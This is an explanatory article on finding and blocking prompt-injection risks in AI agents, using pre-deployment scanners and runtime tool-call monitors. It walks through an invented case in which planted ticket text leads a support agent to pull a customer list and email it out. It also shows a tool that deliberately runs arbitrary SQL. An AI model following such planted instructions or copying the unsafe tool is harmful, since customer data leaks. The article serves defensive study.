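# Scanning AI Agent Code Before Deployment and Enforcing Agent Permissions at Run Time

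## How an agent's tools are wired, and when they can be checked

An AI agent is a program in which a language model chooses actions and ordinary software carries them out. Developers connect the model to functions, called tools, that can look up a customer's order, run a script or send an email. A chatbot with no tools can only produce text. An agent's tool wiring is the code and configuration that determine which tools it has and what data can reach them. The wiring is dangerous when a stranger can influence the model's output and that output goes directly into a powerful tool.

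Before deployment, developers can guard against this with a scanner, a program that examines code and configuration without running the agent and reports connections that look dangerous. While the agent runs, they can use a runtime monitor, which inspects each action before it takes effect and allows or refuses it. Programmers used both techniques on ordinary software long before language models existed. Both are harder to apply to agents, because the link between input and action is a model's output instead of a line of code that somebody wrote.

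### The agent loop

A language model produces text, so it cannot send an email itself. It can request that action with a tool call, which is text in a fixed format that names a tool and gives values for its arguments. Anthropic's *How tool use works* says the model "never runs anything on its own" and describes the arrangement as a contract in which developers specify the operations and the model determines when to request them.

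An agent works in a loop. Its software sends the model the user's message and a list of tools, each with a name, a plain-language description and a schema for its arguments. The model replies with one or more tool calls. The software reads the tool's name and arguments, runs the matching function, adds the output to the conversation and sends the whole conversation back. The model then either makes another call or finishes with an answer. OpenAI's *Function calling* describes the same cycle and tells developers to expect several calls in a single reply.

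The model receives a tool's description and results, but never its code. All new information during a task therefore reaches the model as text added to one growing conversation, called its context. The developer's software normally runs the tools, but Anthropic runs a few, including web search, on its own servers. Those calls usually appear in the developer's software only after they have finished.

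### A support agent with four tools

Take a retailer that builds an agent to handle customer complaints. It needs to read tickets, look up orders in a database, do some arithmetic on refunds and write back to customers. In the style of OpenAI's Agents SDK, a Python library for building agents, the wiring might look like this, with dots in place of the function bodies:

```python
@function_tool
def read_ticket(ticket_id: int) -> str: ...

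@function_tool
def query_orders(sql: str) -> str: ...

@function_tool
def run_python(code: str) -> str: ...

@function_tool
def send_email(to: str, body: str) -> str: ...

support_agent = Agent(
    name="Support agent",
    instructions="Resolve the ticket and reply to the customer.",
    tools=[read_ticket, query_orders, run_python, send_email],
)
```

The line `@function_tool` turns an ordinary function into a tool, and the `tools=[...]` list gives the agent all four. The program doesn't set which tools the agent will use, if any, or in what order. The model determines this separately for each ticket.

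Here the functions sit in the agent's own code. Many agents instead get tools from separate servers through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard that Anthropic introduced in 2024 (Granados, *MCP 2026 changes the rules*, 2026). The specification (Model Context Protocol, 2025) distinguishes a host (the application with the model in it), a client (a connector inside the host) and a server that offers the tools. Under the current rules for tools (Model Context Protocol, *Tools*, 2026), the client sends the server a `tools/list` request to list the available tools and a `tools/call` request to run one. The same document recommends that a human always be able to deny a call. If the retailer moved `query_orders` to such a server, the agent's code would contain an address instead of the function, and the server's operator could change the list of tools after deployment. This setup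 is now common. When MCP's maintainers released the July 2026 version, they counted close to half a billion downloads a month of their main software kits (Model Context Protocol, 2026).

### How a ticket sends an email

Suppose a stranger files ticket 4812, which opens with a complaint about a late parcel. Further down, where a busy support worker would probably not look, the stranger has written instructions for the agent to fetch the names and addresses of recent customers and email them outside the company. A worker then asks the agent to deal with the ticket.

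The model first calls `read_ticket(4812)`, as it should. The software runs the function and adds the full text of the ticket to the context, which now holds the developer's instructions, the worker's request and the stranger's instructions, one after another. If the model follows the stranger's instructions, it next calls `query_orders` with a database query for the customer list. The software runs the query under the company's own database password and returns the rows as text. The model then calls `send_email`, with the stranger's address as `to` and the rows as `body`, and the software sends the message from the company's mail account. Every call has the right format, and every function does what its programmer intended. The attack doesn't need `run_python`, which would let the stranger do much more.

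This is prompt injection, in which the model follows text in the data the agent reads as if it were an instruction. *The Claws in Plain Sight* (2026) distinguishes direct injection, where the attacker types to the model, from indirect injection, where the attacker plants the text in a web page, document, email or tool result that the model later reads. Ticket 4812 is an indirect injection. *The Hitchhiker's Guide to Agentic AI* (2026) credits Greshake and colleagues with the first systematic account of the indirect form and notes that an agent may process dozens of tool outputs in one task, any of which an attacker might have written.

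*Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents* (2026) traces the model's vulnerability to injected text to the lack of any enforced boundary between code and data in an agent's context. Traditional software keeps the two separate. David C, a technical director at Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, makes the same diagnosis for the centre in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*. He compares prompt injection with SQL injection, an older attack in which text typed into a web form runs as a database command. Programmers can prevent SQL injection with parameterised queries, which separate commands from data. A language model has no equivalent setting, since it only predicts the next token (a word or piece of a word) from all the text so far. He thinks it very possible that nobody will ever fully prevent prompt injection.

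The retailer is invented, but researchers at General Analysis described a similar case involving a real product. In their scenario, which Willison relayed in *Supabase MCP can leak your entire SQL database* (2025), text planted in a support ticket leads a coding assistant to expose private database contents to the attacker. Willison calls the underlying combination the "lethal trifecta": access to private data, exposure to text from untrusted people, and a way to send data out. The retailer's support agent has all three, through `query_orders`, `read_ticket` and `send_email`. Supabase, the database company, replied in *Defense in Depth for MCP Servers* that no customer had reported a leak through MCP, and that the risk comes from how models interact with tools, not from the protocol. Both points are compatible with the scenario, which is evidence that the wiring permits the leak but not that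 leaks are happening.

There are also real cases. Inti De Ceukelaire, a security researcher, earned over $50,000 in bug bounties from customer-service chatbots. Some of them could be made to email other people in the company's name, according to Heaton's *Your chatbot can email people on your behalf. Who checked that?* (2026). Underhill's *Cybercriminals Turn to Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks* (2026) reports that criminals are developing tools for indirect injection against agents. Large companies plant instructions too. According to The Hacker News' *Alibaba Cloud Got Caught Prompt-Injecting AI Agents* (2026), Alibaba Cloud sent AI agents prompts that sought data from the user's machine, as a measure against abuse, and has said it will stop.

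### The confused deputy

Security engineers called this kind of fault a "confused deputy" decades before agents. *The Confused Deputy*, a 1988 essay by Hardy, describes a compiler at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. The compiler had permission to write files in its own directory so that it could record usage statistics there. Users could also name a file to receive debugging output. One user named the company's billing file, which was in the same directory. The operating system confirmed that the compiler was allowed to write there and let it overwrite the billing records.

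The user had no permission to write to the billing file, but the compiler did, and it wrote to the file on the user's behalf. A confused deputy is a program tricked in this way into using its own authority for someone else. Hardy explains that the compiler had authority from two sources, its own licence and the user who ran it, and could not specify which one it was using for a given write. His remedy was a capability, a token that identifies a file and grants permission to use it. The compiler would write its statistics with its own token and the debugging output with whatever token the user had supplied. A user without a token for the billing file could not have made the compiler write to it.

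The support agent holds the company's database password and mail account, and it takes text from anyone who can file a ticket. Its situation closely resembles the compiler's, but the compiler's remedy only partly applies. A programmer can give a compiler the means to keep its two authorities separate. David C calls a language model an "inherently confusable deputy" because nothing reliably ties a given tool call to the part of the context that prompted it. He advises designers to assume that some injections will succeed and to use ordinary deterministic code to limit what the agent can then do.

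The crudest safeguard is to remove tools. *The Hitchhiker's Guide to Agentic AI* says, "An agent that cannot send email cannot be hijacked into sending email." The retailer could perhaps drop `run_python` and calculate refunds some other way, but it can't drop `send_email` because the agent has to reply to customers. *AttriGuard* (2026) points out that removing tools doesn't help when the attacker's task uses the same tools as the user's. For example, a normal run on ticket 4812 and a hijacked one may both read the ticket, query the orders and send one email. They differ in what data they query, what the email contains and where they send it.

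### Two moments for a check

Before deployment, a scanner can inspect only how the agent's tools are wired, because there are no tickets or model outputs yet. It looks for a route from a source, where untrusted data enters the program, to a sink, an operation that is dangerous if that data reaches it. In the support agent, the source is the text that `read_ticket` returns, and the sinks are the `to` and `body` of `send_email`, the `code` of `run_python` and the `sql` of `query_orders`. This search is called taint analysis, and in ordinary programs it follows data through assignments and function calls. That would find nothing here, because no line of the agent's code passes a ticket to `send_email`; the model makes that connection while the agent is running.

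A scanner for agents has to work from the declarations instead. *AGENTFLOW* (Wang, Hou and colleagues, 2026) presents one that reads constructs such as `tools=[...]` and draws a graph of which prompts can influence which agents and which agents can call which tools. The scanner reports a path when a prompt can influence an agent that can fill in the arguments of a sensitive tool. Since the code doesn't determine what the model will do, the scanner treats every call that the wiring permits as possible.

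The graph also records guards. A guard is code that restricts a dangerous operation, such as an allowlist of recipients or an approval step. In the Agents SDK a developer can add one by changing a single line above `send_email`:

```python
@function_tool(needs_approval=True)
```

According to OpenAI's *Guardrails and human review*, this setting pauses the run when the model calls the tool, and the run continues only after the application approves or rejects the call. A scanner can detect the setting, but it can't determine from the code whether the person who approves a call will have read the address.

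A run-time check belongs in the agent's loop, after it receives a call and before it runs the tool. Developers don't always leave room for a check there. The helper in Anthropic's *Tool runner (SDK)* runs each tool as soon as the model calls it, and Anthropic directs developers who want human approval or conditional execution to write the loop themselves. A runtime monitor checks each call at this point against a policy, a set of rules about which calls may run. For the retailer, one rule might be that `send_email` may write only to the customer who opened the ticket. When the hijacked model tries to email an outsider, the monitor compares `to` with the address on ticket 4812 and blocks the call because they don't match.

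The monitor does not need to determine why the model made the call or recognise the planted text as an attack. AWS's *AGENTSEC02-BP01 Implement tool authorization* recommends a deterministic check outside the model, before the tool executes, "regardless of how the agent arrived at the call". AWS considers a rule written only into the prompt insufficient because an injected instruction can override it. Its sample rule allows clinicians to reschedule appointments only for patients on their own list.

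A scanner can report that tickets may influence outgoing email on the day the retailer finishes the code, before any customer has written in. The recipient's address isn't available until the model tries to use it, so only the monitor can check it.

### Counting the errors

Scanners and monitors can each make two kinds of error. A false positive is a harmless path that a scanner reports or a harmless action that a monitor refuses. A false negative is a dangerous path that a scanner misses or a harmful action that a monitor allows. Three rates summarise these errors, and a worked case shows how much they can differ.

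Suppose a company's agents contain 200 paths from a source to a sink, of which 10 are dangerous. A scanner reports 20 suspected problems, called findings, and 8 of them are correct.

| | Dangerous | Harmless | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Reported | 8 | 12 | 20 |
| Not reported | 2 | 178 | 180 |
| Total | 10 | 190 | 200 |

Precision, the share of reports that are right, is 8/20, or 40%. Recall, the share of real problems that the scanner reports, is 8/10, or 80%. The false-positive rate, the share of harmless paths that the scanner reports, is 12/190, or 6.3%.

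A vendor could truthfully advertise a false-positive rate of about 6% for a scanner even though 60% of its findings are wrong. Harmless paths outnumber dangerous ones by 19 to 1, so flagging even a small share of them produces more false findings than real ones. Precision therefore depends on the code being scanned as well as on the scanner. If 100 of the 200 paths were dangerous and the scanner kept the same recall and false-positive rate, it would report 80 real problems and about 6 harmless paths, and its precision would be 93%.

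Recall is harder to measure than precision because someone has to find the problems the scanner missed. Wang and colleagues checked 100 of AGENTFLOW's reports by hand and judged 73 to be right, a precision of 73%. They also examined 100 agents that had powerful tools but no report, and found 9 missed risks. Recall can't be calculated from these figures without knowing how many unreported agents there were in all and how many risks they contained.

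The unit of counting matters just as much. AGENTFLOW found 4,357 risky paths, all in 238 of the 5,399 projects it analysed, or about 18 per affected project. A scanner's unit is a path in the code, which somebody reviews once and perhaps again when the code changes. A monitor's unit is a call or a session, meaning all the calls in one task. If a monitor wrongly refuses 1% of harmless calls and a typical ticket takes four calls, about 3.9% of harmless sessions will hit at least one wrongful refusal, provided the errors are independent. At a thousand harmless tickets a day, about 39 customers would have their complaints stalled. One dangerous path may carry no harmful calls in a year or several thousand in an afternoon. A scanner's 6.3% false-positive rate and a monitor's 1% rate are therefore shares of different things, and the lower rate doesn't make the monitor more accurate.

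## The case for scanning agent code before deployment

Advocates of scanning think an early check is most valuable for code that seldom runs. Suppose the programmers gave the agent `run_python` only for refunds in a foreign currency. That branch might not run for months. A runtime monitor can't inspect the branch until it runs, and a test suite misses it unless somebody wrote a test for it. A scanner reads the branch before deployment, along with the rest of the file.

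Scanning also adds no overhead to tool calls. A monitor has to run every time the agent uses a tool, whereas a scanner runs when the code changes, so customers don't wait for it. Somebody has to read the findings, but that work grows with the amount of code, not the number of tickets.

A scan can list which agents can reach which tools, and a company with two hundred agents written by different teams may well not have such a list. A scan can also lead to a repair, because a programmer who has read a finding can rewrite the tool so that no ticket can produce a hijacked query. A monitor that refuses such a query at run time leaves the tool unchanged for the next ticket.

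Most of the flaws found in MCP servers so far are the kind that scanners look for. Shi, Fu and colleagues (2026), in *Mitigating Taint-Style Vulnerabilities in MCP Servers via Security-Aware Tool Descriptions*, collected 53 known vulnerabilities in 45 servers and classed 81% of them as taint-style, meaning that untrusted input reaches a dangerous operation. That share may be high partly because researchers who search with taint analysis will mostly find taint-style flaws.

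### Following `query_orders` through a scanner

Zhang, Nian and Zhao (2026), in *AGENT AUDIT*, describe an open-source scanner for agents written in Python. Its steps are easiest to follow on `query_orders`, whose body the retailer might have written like this:

```python
@function_tool
def query_orders(sql: str) -> str:
    cursor = orders_db.cursor()
    cursor.execute(sql)
    return str(cursor.fetchall())
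```

Agent Audit first looks for tool functions. It recognises 12 ways of declaring one across LangChain, CrewAI and custom code, and we assume here that `@function_tool` is among them. A finding inside a tool starts with a higher confidence score (0.90) than one in an ordinary function (0.55) because a model may have written the tool's arguments.

The scanner then marks every parameter of the function as a source, so it treats `sql` as tainted, meaning that its value may contain untrusted text. Next it parses the function and records where each value goes. Here, `sql` goes directly into `cursor.execute`.

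Agent Audit looks along the trail for code that checks a value or makes it safe, and multiplies the score by 0.20 if it finds any. Finally, it searches the recorded links to test whether a tainted value reaches a sink, such as `cursor.execute`, which runs a database query, or `eval`, which runs a string as Python. In `query_orders`, the tainted value reaches a sink and nothing along the trail lowers the score, so the finding stays at 0.90 unless another adjustment changes it. That makes it a warning, just below the 0.92 at which Agent Audit assigns its top level, "block".

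The programmer can respond by taking the query away from the model:

```python
@function_tool
def query_orders(customer_id: int) -> str:
    cursor = orders_db.cursor()
    cursor.execute(
        "SELECT id, status, total FROM orders WHERE customer_id = ?",
        (customer_id,),
    )
    return str(cursor.fetchall())
```

This is a parameterised query, so the model can supply a customer number but no SQL. The score drops to 0.90 × 0.20 = 0.18, and Agent Audit suppresses anything below 0.30. The stranger behind ticket 4812 can no longer get the whole customer list in one call. But a hijacked model could still look up other customers' orders one number at a time, and the scanner would not flag it. To prevent those lookups, the programmer has to take the customer number from the ticket's record instead of letting the model fill it in.

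A call to `isinstance()`, which checks a value's type, earns the same discount as a parameterised query. That makes sense when the check admits only whole numbers, but a check that `sql` is a string would let every possible query through.

Repairs can fail too. Shi and colleagues describe a server that converts web pages to text. Its maintainers patched a taint-style flaw, but a user pointed out that attackers could still get around the new check. Shi and colleagues conclude that code patches are piecemeal, and propose instead adding security warnings to the tools' descriptions and having the model review its own calls. With these defenses, only 0.13% of attacks succeeded in their tests. That rate is low, but the protection consists of text that the model has to follow, and prompt injection works by changing which text the model follows. Repairing the code avoids this weakness because a repaired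 function behaves the same way whatever the model has read.

Agent Audit follows data only within one function. If `query_orders` passed `sql` to a helper that ran the query, Agent Audit would stop tracking `sql` at the helper. Cisco designed the code analysis in its MCP Scanner for that situation. It treats all tool parameters as untrusted and follows them across functions and files.

### Settings, passwords and tool descriptions

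Some hazards are in files that contain no code. Suppose the retailer connects its agent to an MCP server through a settings file that gives the server access to the entire disk and contains the database password in plain text. A general code scanner may not interpret the settings in such a file. Agent Audit parses nine formats of MCP settings and checks them for problems such as overly broad file access, servers from unverified sources, missing authentication and missing sandboxes (enclosures that limit what a program can touch).

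The scanner searches separately for passwords by comparing text with more than 40 patterns for keys, tokens and database addresses. It measures how random each match is, so that a placeholder such as `your-key-here` doesn't count, and it lowers the score for matches in test and example files. Zhang and colleagues argue that runtime filters can't deal with this kind of exposure. They have a point, because a thief who copies the password from the settings file can log in to the database without the agent making a tool call.

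Tool descriptions are another place to hide an attack, because the model reads them to choose tools. A malicious server can put instructions in a description, or offer a tool with almost the same name as a trusted one. Agent Audit's `inspect` command connects to a running server, fetches its tool list and searches the descriptions for text that overrides instructions or sends data elsewhere. It also compares tool names across servers by counting the letters that differ. The command doesn't run any of the tools, and its result applies only to the descriptions the server sent during that inspection.

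Even an honest description gives little information about what a tool can do. Of the 1,856 descriptions that Shi and colleagues collected from 100 popular servers, 65% stated only the tool's basic function, and only 7% gave any guidance on security. Several scanners therefore examine the code. Cisco's is meant to compare the description with what the code does, so it should flag a tool for checking email addresses if the tool also uploads the address book. *ACaM* (2026) derives each tool's capabilities from its source code, and uses a language model only for the few that program analysis can't settle. The model's answer can never weaken a fact established by the analysis.

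### How well Agent Audit did

Zhang and colleagues tested their scanner on 22 samples of agent code and configuration containing 42 flaws that experts had marked. They ran two general-purpose code scanners, Semgrep and Bandit, on the same samples.

| | Agent Audit | Semgrep | Bandit |
|---|---|---|---|
| Flaws found | 40 | 10 | 11 |
| False positives | 6 | 0 | 0 |
| Published recall | 95.2% | 23.8% | 29.7% |

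Zhang and colleagues list 11 flaws that Bandit found and 26 that it missed, so its recall is out of 37 flaws, while the other two are out of 42. If all 42 were counted, Bandit's recall would be 26.2%, which wouldn't change the ranking.

It matters more that the same team built the scanner and the test. Of the 42 flaws, 10 are in MCP settings, where Semgrep found none, and 12 are exposed credentials, of which it found one. The other 20 are flaws in code. Semgrep found 9 of these, and Agent Audit found at least 19, since one of its two misses was a credential. Agent Audit's lead on flaws in code is therefore about two to one, rather than the published four to one. The test does show that general scanners miss whole categories of agent flaws. It is weaker evidence that Agent Audit would find 95% of the flaws in other teams' agents, because its rules and the test reflect the same team's idea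 of what to look for.

All six false positives came from the rules for MCP settings, which flagged safe configurations. The scanner took 0.87 seconds to check 22,009 lines of Python, which is fast enough to run on every code change and block any release that fails the scan.

### A graph of what each agent can reach

Agent Audit's data-flow analysis can establish that `query_orders` accepts arbitrary SQL, but not that the same agent reads strangers' tickets and sends email, because those facts are in other functions and in the agent's tool list. AgentFlow, a graph-drawing scanner by Wang and colleagues, starts from that list.

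The graph has three kinds of edges. Component edges record what belongs to what, so they connect `support_agent` to its instructions, model and four tools. Control-flow edges record what can trigger what, so one runs from the agent to `send_email`. If the developer has required approval, one edge runs from the agent to the approval step and another from there to the tool. Data-flow edges record where information can travel. One carries the text that `read_ticket` returns to the agent, and another carries the agent's output into the arguments of `send_email`.

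Control and data edges can also connect agents. In Wang and colleagues' example, a research agent can search the web and hand its task to an operations agent, which can send email. The research agent has no email tool, so a reviewer who looked at it alone might see no danger in a hostile web page. But the graph shows that the page's text can travel from the research agent to the operations agent and into an email.

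To find risks, AgentFlow searches the graph for triples of a prompt *p*, an agent *a* and a sensitive tool *c*:

```text
report (p, a, c) if
    a is reachable from p along data-flow edges, and
    c is reachable from a along control-flow edges, and
    a data-flow edge runs from a into the arguments of c
```

This definition includes paths that pass through an approval step, so a reviewer has to decide whether the approval is good enough. A tool without arguments, such as one that cancels every open order, would not meet the third condition, however much harm it could do. The search also starts from prompts and instructions, not tool results. For the support agent, it would identify `send_email` as the tool at risk, but would trace the path from the worker's request instead of the stranger's ticket.

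The component edges supply the inventory. AgentFlow completed 98 of 100 sampled projects and listed 2,295 components with 1,008 links between them. Trusera's competing tool listed 3,615 items, most of them models and software packages, with no links. A longer list isn't necessarily more accurate, and AgentFlow's links show which agents can call `send_email`, which a security team is likely to ask. Inventories are hard to use without this kind of structure. *Beyond Predefined Sinks* (2026), for example, counted 23,866 candidate sensitive operations in 67 repositories. *Data Leakage Prevention in Agentic Applications via Preemptive Hardening* (2026) also uses a language model to classify whether each handoff between agents carries data or instructions. Text from a stranger is more dangerous if the next agent receives it as an instruction.

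### What the audit of AgentFlow found

AgentFlow reported risks in 238 projects, 4.4% of those that Wang and colleagues analysed. In 129 of the 238, the agent could send data out, in 74 it could touch files, in 42 it could query a database, and in 41 it could run commands or code. Half of the scans finished within about 14 seconds.

The researchers checked a sample of 100 AgentFlow reports and judged 27 of them wrong. In 25 of those 27, the path AgentFlow had drawn existed, but AgentFlow had wrongly classed the tool at the end of it as dangerous. Thirteen of these tools only read local files, seven ran read-only database queries and five were restricted calculators. If AgentFlow had left out those 25 reports, 73 of the remaining 75 would have been right, or 97%.

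That calculation depends on the reviewers' view of harm. They counted a read-only query as harmless because it can't change or delete anything, but the danger of a sink depends partly on what else the agent can do. The attack in ticket 4812 needs only a read-only query to fetch the customer list, which `send_email` then sends out. If a scanner dropped read-only queries from its list of sinks, its measured precision would rise, but it would miss half of this attack on an agent that has both tools.

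The scanner missed nine risks among 100 unreported agents with powerful tools. That 9% is a share of unreported agents, most of which had no risk to miss. It is therefore not the false-negative rate, which is the share of real risks that a scanner misses.

Recall depends heavily on how many agents had powerful tools and no report, a total that Wang and colleagues don't give. Suppose AgentFlow's correct reports covered 300 risky agents. If another 500 agents had powerful tools and no report, 9% of them would be 45 missed risks, and recall would be 300 out of 345, or 87%. If there were 5,000 such agents, 450 risks would be missed and recall would be 40%. The published figures fit either case. They also use different units, since the findings are paths and the sample of unreported cases consists of agents.

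Most of AgentFlow's misses occurred in code where developers had wrapped commands in their own functions, attached tools at run time, or coordinated agents in ways that none of the five supported frameworks defines. AgentFlow recognizes 143 framework constructs and is less effective on agents built in other ways.

### Whether the trail ends at the model

Ordinary taint analysis can't trace untrusted text through a model call. Xu, Cheng and colleagues (2026), in *Reachability Across the NL/PL Boundary*, write the call as *o* = *M*(*T*[*p*₁, …, *pₙ*]), where *T* is a prompt template, the *p*s are values that the program inserts into it, and *o* is the output. An analyser can work out which inputs affect an ordinary function's output, but it can't do this for *M*, which has no readable code that turns its input into its output. According to Xu and colleagues, established tools such as CodeQL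 and Semgrep never mark the model's output as a taint source.

One approach is to treat everything the model produces as tainted. Agent Audit does this in effect when it marks a tool's parameters as sources, because it then starts tracking data from the model's output. *TaintP2X*, by He, Wang and colleagues, applies the idea to any program that calls a language model. Its scanner recognises 97 standard ways of calling one, uses a language model to find developers' wrappers around these calls, and follows the output to 236 kinds of sink. It found 27 of 35 known vulnerabilities.

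The data-flow analysis with the extra sources also produces many false positives. Across 4,772 repositories, it flagged 263 candidate flaws, of which 95 were real. TaintP2X then has a language model discard candidates where no outsider can influence the prompt or where the code already makes the output safe. That left 114 findings, 78 of them real, so precision rose from 36% to 68%. He and colleagues report that this step removed four real flaws, although the number of real findings fell by 17. They submitted 40 issues to the projects' maintainers, who had confirmed seven by the time of publication.

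The other approach, which Xu and colleagues take in a system called PRISM, is to model how a prompt's contents reach the output. Language models examine what happened to each inserted value in an actual output and label it from a list of 25 options, such as copied, paraphrased, summarised, reduced to a yes or no, or ignored. Four of the labels mean that nothing from the value reached the output. If a value has only those labels, PRISM drops the path. Otherwise, a language model reads the code after the call and judges whether the output reaches the sink.

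Xu and colleagues tested this on 353 pairs of an inserted value and a sink, 110 of which reviewers had judged to be real paths. Treating every output as tainted catches all 110 but also produces 243 false reports, a precision of 31.2%. PRISM's best version found 103 of the 110 with 39 false reports, a precision of 72.5% and a recall of 93.6%. Language models asked to judge the entire path at once had slightly lower precision, at 58% to 70%, but their recall was only 39% to 68%.

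The labels probably account for only a small part of the drop in false reports. Of the full set of 8,119 values that Xu and colleagues labelled, just 7% were completely blocked, so a filter that removes blocked values can't remove much. Most of the drop must come from the separate reading of the code after the call.

A deeper problem is that the labels describe what a model did with ordinary values, while an attacker writes text so that the model won't ignore it. The labels also depend on the model. When Xu and colleagues tried to reproduce past prompt-injection flaws in OpenClaw, a personal AI assistant, on two models, only six still worked, because safety training had stopped the rest. A company that relied on such labels would need to redo them whenever it changed models. In the support agent, the labels would save little work anyway, since the retailer puts tickets in the prompt so that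 the model will act on them, which makes assuming the worst close to the truth.

### Testing the findings with real prompts

A developer can also sort real findings from false ones by attacking the agent before release. Liu, Zhang and colleagues built AgentFuzz to do this in *Make Agent Defeat Agent*. The tool first used static analysis to find 828 places in 20 popular open-source agents where the code performs a dangerous operation. It then ran the agents, sent prompts intended to reach each place, and adjusted the prompts according to how close they had come. All 34 flaws it reported were real.

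An earlier tool, LLMSmith, reports chains of function calls that lead from a user's input to a sink. On the same 20 agents, it found 10 of the real flaws and produced 332 false positives. Some of the false positives involved values that no user could control, or checks in the code that LLMSmith didn't detect. Others came from the way agents call their tools. A typical program looks up a tool by the name the model outputs and calls a generic `run` function on it, so the code doesn't specify which function will run. LLMSmith inferred the function by matching names, which connected unrelated functions and missed some real connections.

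AgentFuzz lacks some of scanning's advantages. It needs a working copy of each agent and a model to run it, and testing 20 agents took 69 hours of processor time. A successful attack proves a flaw, but AgentFuzz spends at most five minutes on each place, so failed attempts are much weaker evidence that a place is safe. Liu and colleagues put the tool's recall at 97%, but they measured it against a list of 35 flaws, 34 of which AgentFuzz itself had found. They also reviewed 83 of the 794 places that AgentFuzz had not reported, and one was vulnerable. At that rate, the 794 places would contain about ten flaws, and recall would be nearer 77%. AgentFlow's figures don't allow a similar estimate because they don't include the total. The estimate for AgentFuzz rests on a single miss, so the true figure could be much higher or lower.

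## The case for checking every tool call at run time

The argument for a runtime monitor starts from prompt injection, in which text that an agent reads steers its model. Nobody knows which tool calls the model will make until it makes them, but a call does no harm until the agent's software runs it. Advocates conclude that the software should decide whether to allow each call just before running it, without relying on the model's judgement.

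In *Agentao*, Jin, Jiao and Tong (2026) built an agent runtime in which the model proposes actions and the host application authorises them. They claim that explicit permissions and records make an agent easier to control and inspect, but they don't offer a formal guarantee of safety.

In *Progent*, Shi, He and colleagues (2025) give a practical reason for checking tool calls. Ordinary code can't reliably judge a model's free-text reasoning, but it can compare a tool call's name and typed arguments with a rule. They also argue that all of an agent's external effects pass through tool calls. That is true of the software, but an agent's written answer can do harm too. If the text planted in ticket 4812 led the model to tell the support worker that the customer was owed a large refund, and the worker paid it, the monitor would have had no bad call to refuse. Shi, He and colleagues place attacks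 of this kind outside Progent's scope.

### Anderson's reference monitor

Security engineers have worked with this idea for over fifty years. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972), a report for the US Air Force, described a reference monitor, which checks each attempt by a program to use a file or other resource against a record of what that program may do. The report required the monitor to check every access, be tamper-proof, and be small enough to verify.

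A rule in the support agent's prompt, such as "only email the customer who opened the ticket", fails all three. The model may not apply it, text in a ticket may persuade the model to ignore it, and nobody can verify a model with billions of parameters. A check in ordinary code can do much better. It treats the attacker's text only as a value to compare, so instructions in that text can't change the rule. Progent's procedure for deciding a call takes eight lines of pseudocode, but the working version also relies on a library for checking data formats and on a logic solver, which somebody would also have to trust or verify. Whether every call passes through the monitor depends on where developers install it.

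The monitor also needs a policy. The simplest policies look only at the call in front of the monitor.

### Rules on the call itself

A Progent policy is a list of rules. Each rule names a tool, allows or forbids calls to it, and can set conditions on the arguments. The monitor applies the "forbid" rules first and refuses any call that no rule allows. Suppose the address on ticket 4812 is `j.reed@example.com`, and `query_orders` still accepts any SQL. In the notation of the Progent paper, slightly simplified, the retailer might write:

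```text
allow read_ticket  when { ticket_id == 4812 }
allow query_orders when { true }
allow send_email   when { to == "j.reed@example.com" }
```

The policy gives these decisions:

| Call | Decision | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| `send_email` to `drop@example.net` | Refuse | The recipient doesn't match |
| `run_python` with any code | Refuse | No rule allows the tool |
| `send_email` to `j.reed@example.com` | Allow | The recipient matches |

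When Progent blocks a tool call, by default it returns an error message that includes the reason and instructs the model to continue with the user's task. A hijacked agent may therefore still write the reply the user asked for. A developer can instead set Progent to stop the agent or ask the user.

The stranger opened ticket 4812, so the policy allows email to the stranger's address. If the planted instructions lead the agent to email the customer list there, the monitor will let the email through, because the rule doesn't restrict the body. Shi, He and colleagues acknowledge that Progent can't stop an attack that stays within the permissions the task needs.

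The retailer can shrink those permissions if its tools are narrow enough. With the repaired `query_orders`, which takes a customer number instead of SQL, the second rule could become:

```text
allow query_orders when { customer_id == 20417 }
```

Now the agent can fetch only one customer's orders. The rule also stops a hijacked model from looking up other customers one number at a time, which the repair alone did not prevent. No equally simple rule exists for `run_python`, whose only argument is an entire program.

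AgentSpec, which Wang, Poskitt and Sun (2025), in *AgentSpec*, present, attaches its rules to events. A rule has a trigger, a condition and a response:

```text
rule @outside_recipient
trigger send_email
check !is_ticket_customer
enforce user_inspection
end
```

Here `is_ticket_customer` is a Python function the developer supplies. If the recipient isn't the ticket's customer, AgentSpec pauses and asks the user. It can also stop the agent, run another action, or have a language model reconsider. That last option returns the decision to a model, which the monitor was meant to avoid.

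AgentSpec's tests on code show how hard it is to judge a program from its text. Wang, Poskitt and Sun gave a coding agent risky instructions from a benchmark called RedCode-Exec and checked each Python program before it ran. The rules flagged 333 of the 422 programs in their published table, or 79%. They report a rate of over 90%, which fits the table if one leaves out two categories in which the agent's programs turned out not to contain the flaw. Reviewers then judged 58 of the flagged programs harmless and let them run. For one rule, which looks for programs that fetch and print material from untrusted websites, the researchers suggest that the monitor would be more accurate if it used data-flow analysis, the scanner's main technique.

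### Rules on earlier calls

A monitor can also record what the agent has already done. AgentSpec rules can depend on the agent's past steps, so the retailer could block `send_email` once `query_orders` has returned rows about anyone except the ticket's customer. This fixes the flaw in the policy above even if `query_orders` still accepts any SQL. The stranger's address is still an allowed recipient, but the agent can no longer email anyone after reading the customer list.

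History rules can count calls as well. A sample policy in *Guardrails as Infrastructure* (Sigdel and Baral, 2026) limits an agent to ten shell commands a minute. A limit of one email per ticket would keep a hijacked support agent from writing to a thousand people. A rule can also require an earlier call, for example by blocking changes to any record the agent hasn't read in the current session.

These rules can block harmless replies. Suppose a customer's parcel went to a neighbour who is also a customer, and the agent looks up the neighbour's order to sort it out. The history rule would then block the agent's reply to the first customer, even if it didn't mention the neighbour, because the monitor records that the agent read the rows but not where their contents went.

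### Labels that follow the data

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) presents FIDES, a system that tracks where data goes by attaching two labels to each piece. An integrity label marks the data as trusted or untrusted, and a confidentiality label lists who may read it. When the agent combines data, the result is untrusted if any part is, and only people who may read every part may read it.

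Say that staff and the customer who placed an order may read that order's row. The readers of the whole customer list are then the people who appear in every row's label:

```text
readers(list) = {staff, customer 1} ∩ {staff, customer 2} ∩ ... = {staff}
```

FIDES can block an email unless every recipient is allowed to read its contents. The stranger isn't on the staff, so the monitor blocks any email sending them the list, whichever address the ticket gives. It would still allow an email to the stranger about their own order. The retailer doesn't have to write a separate rule for each ticket.

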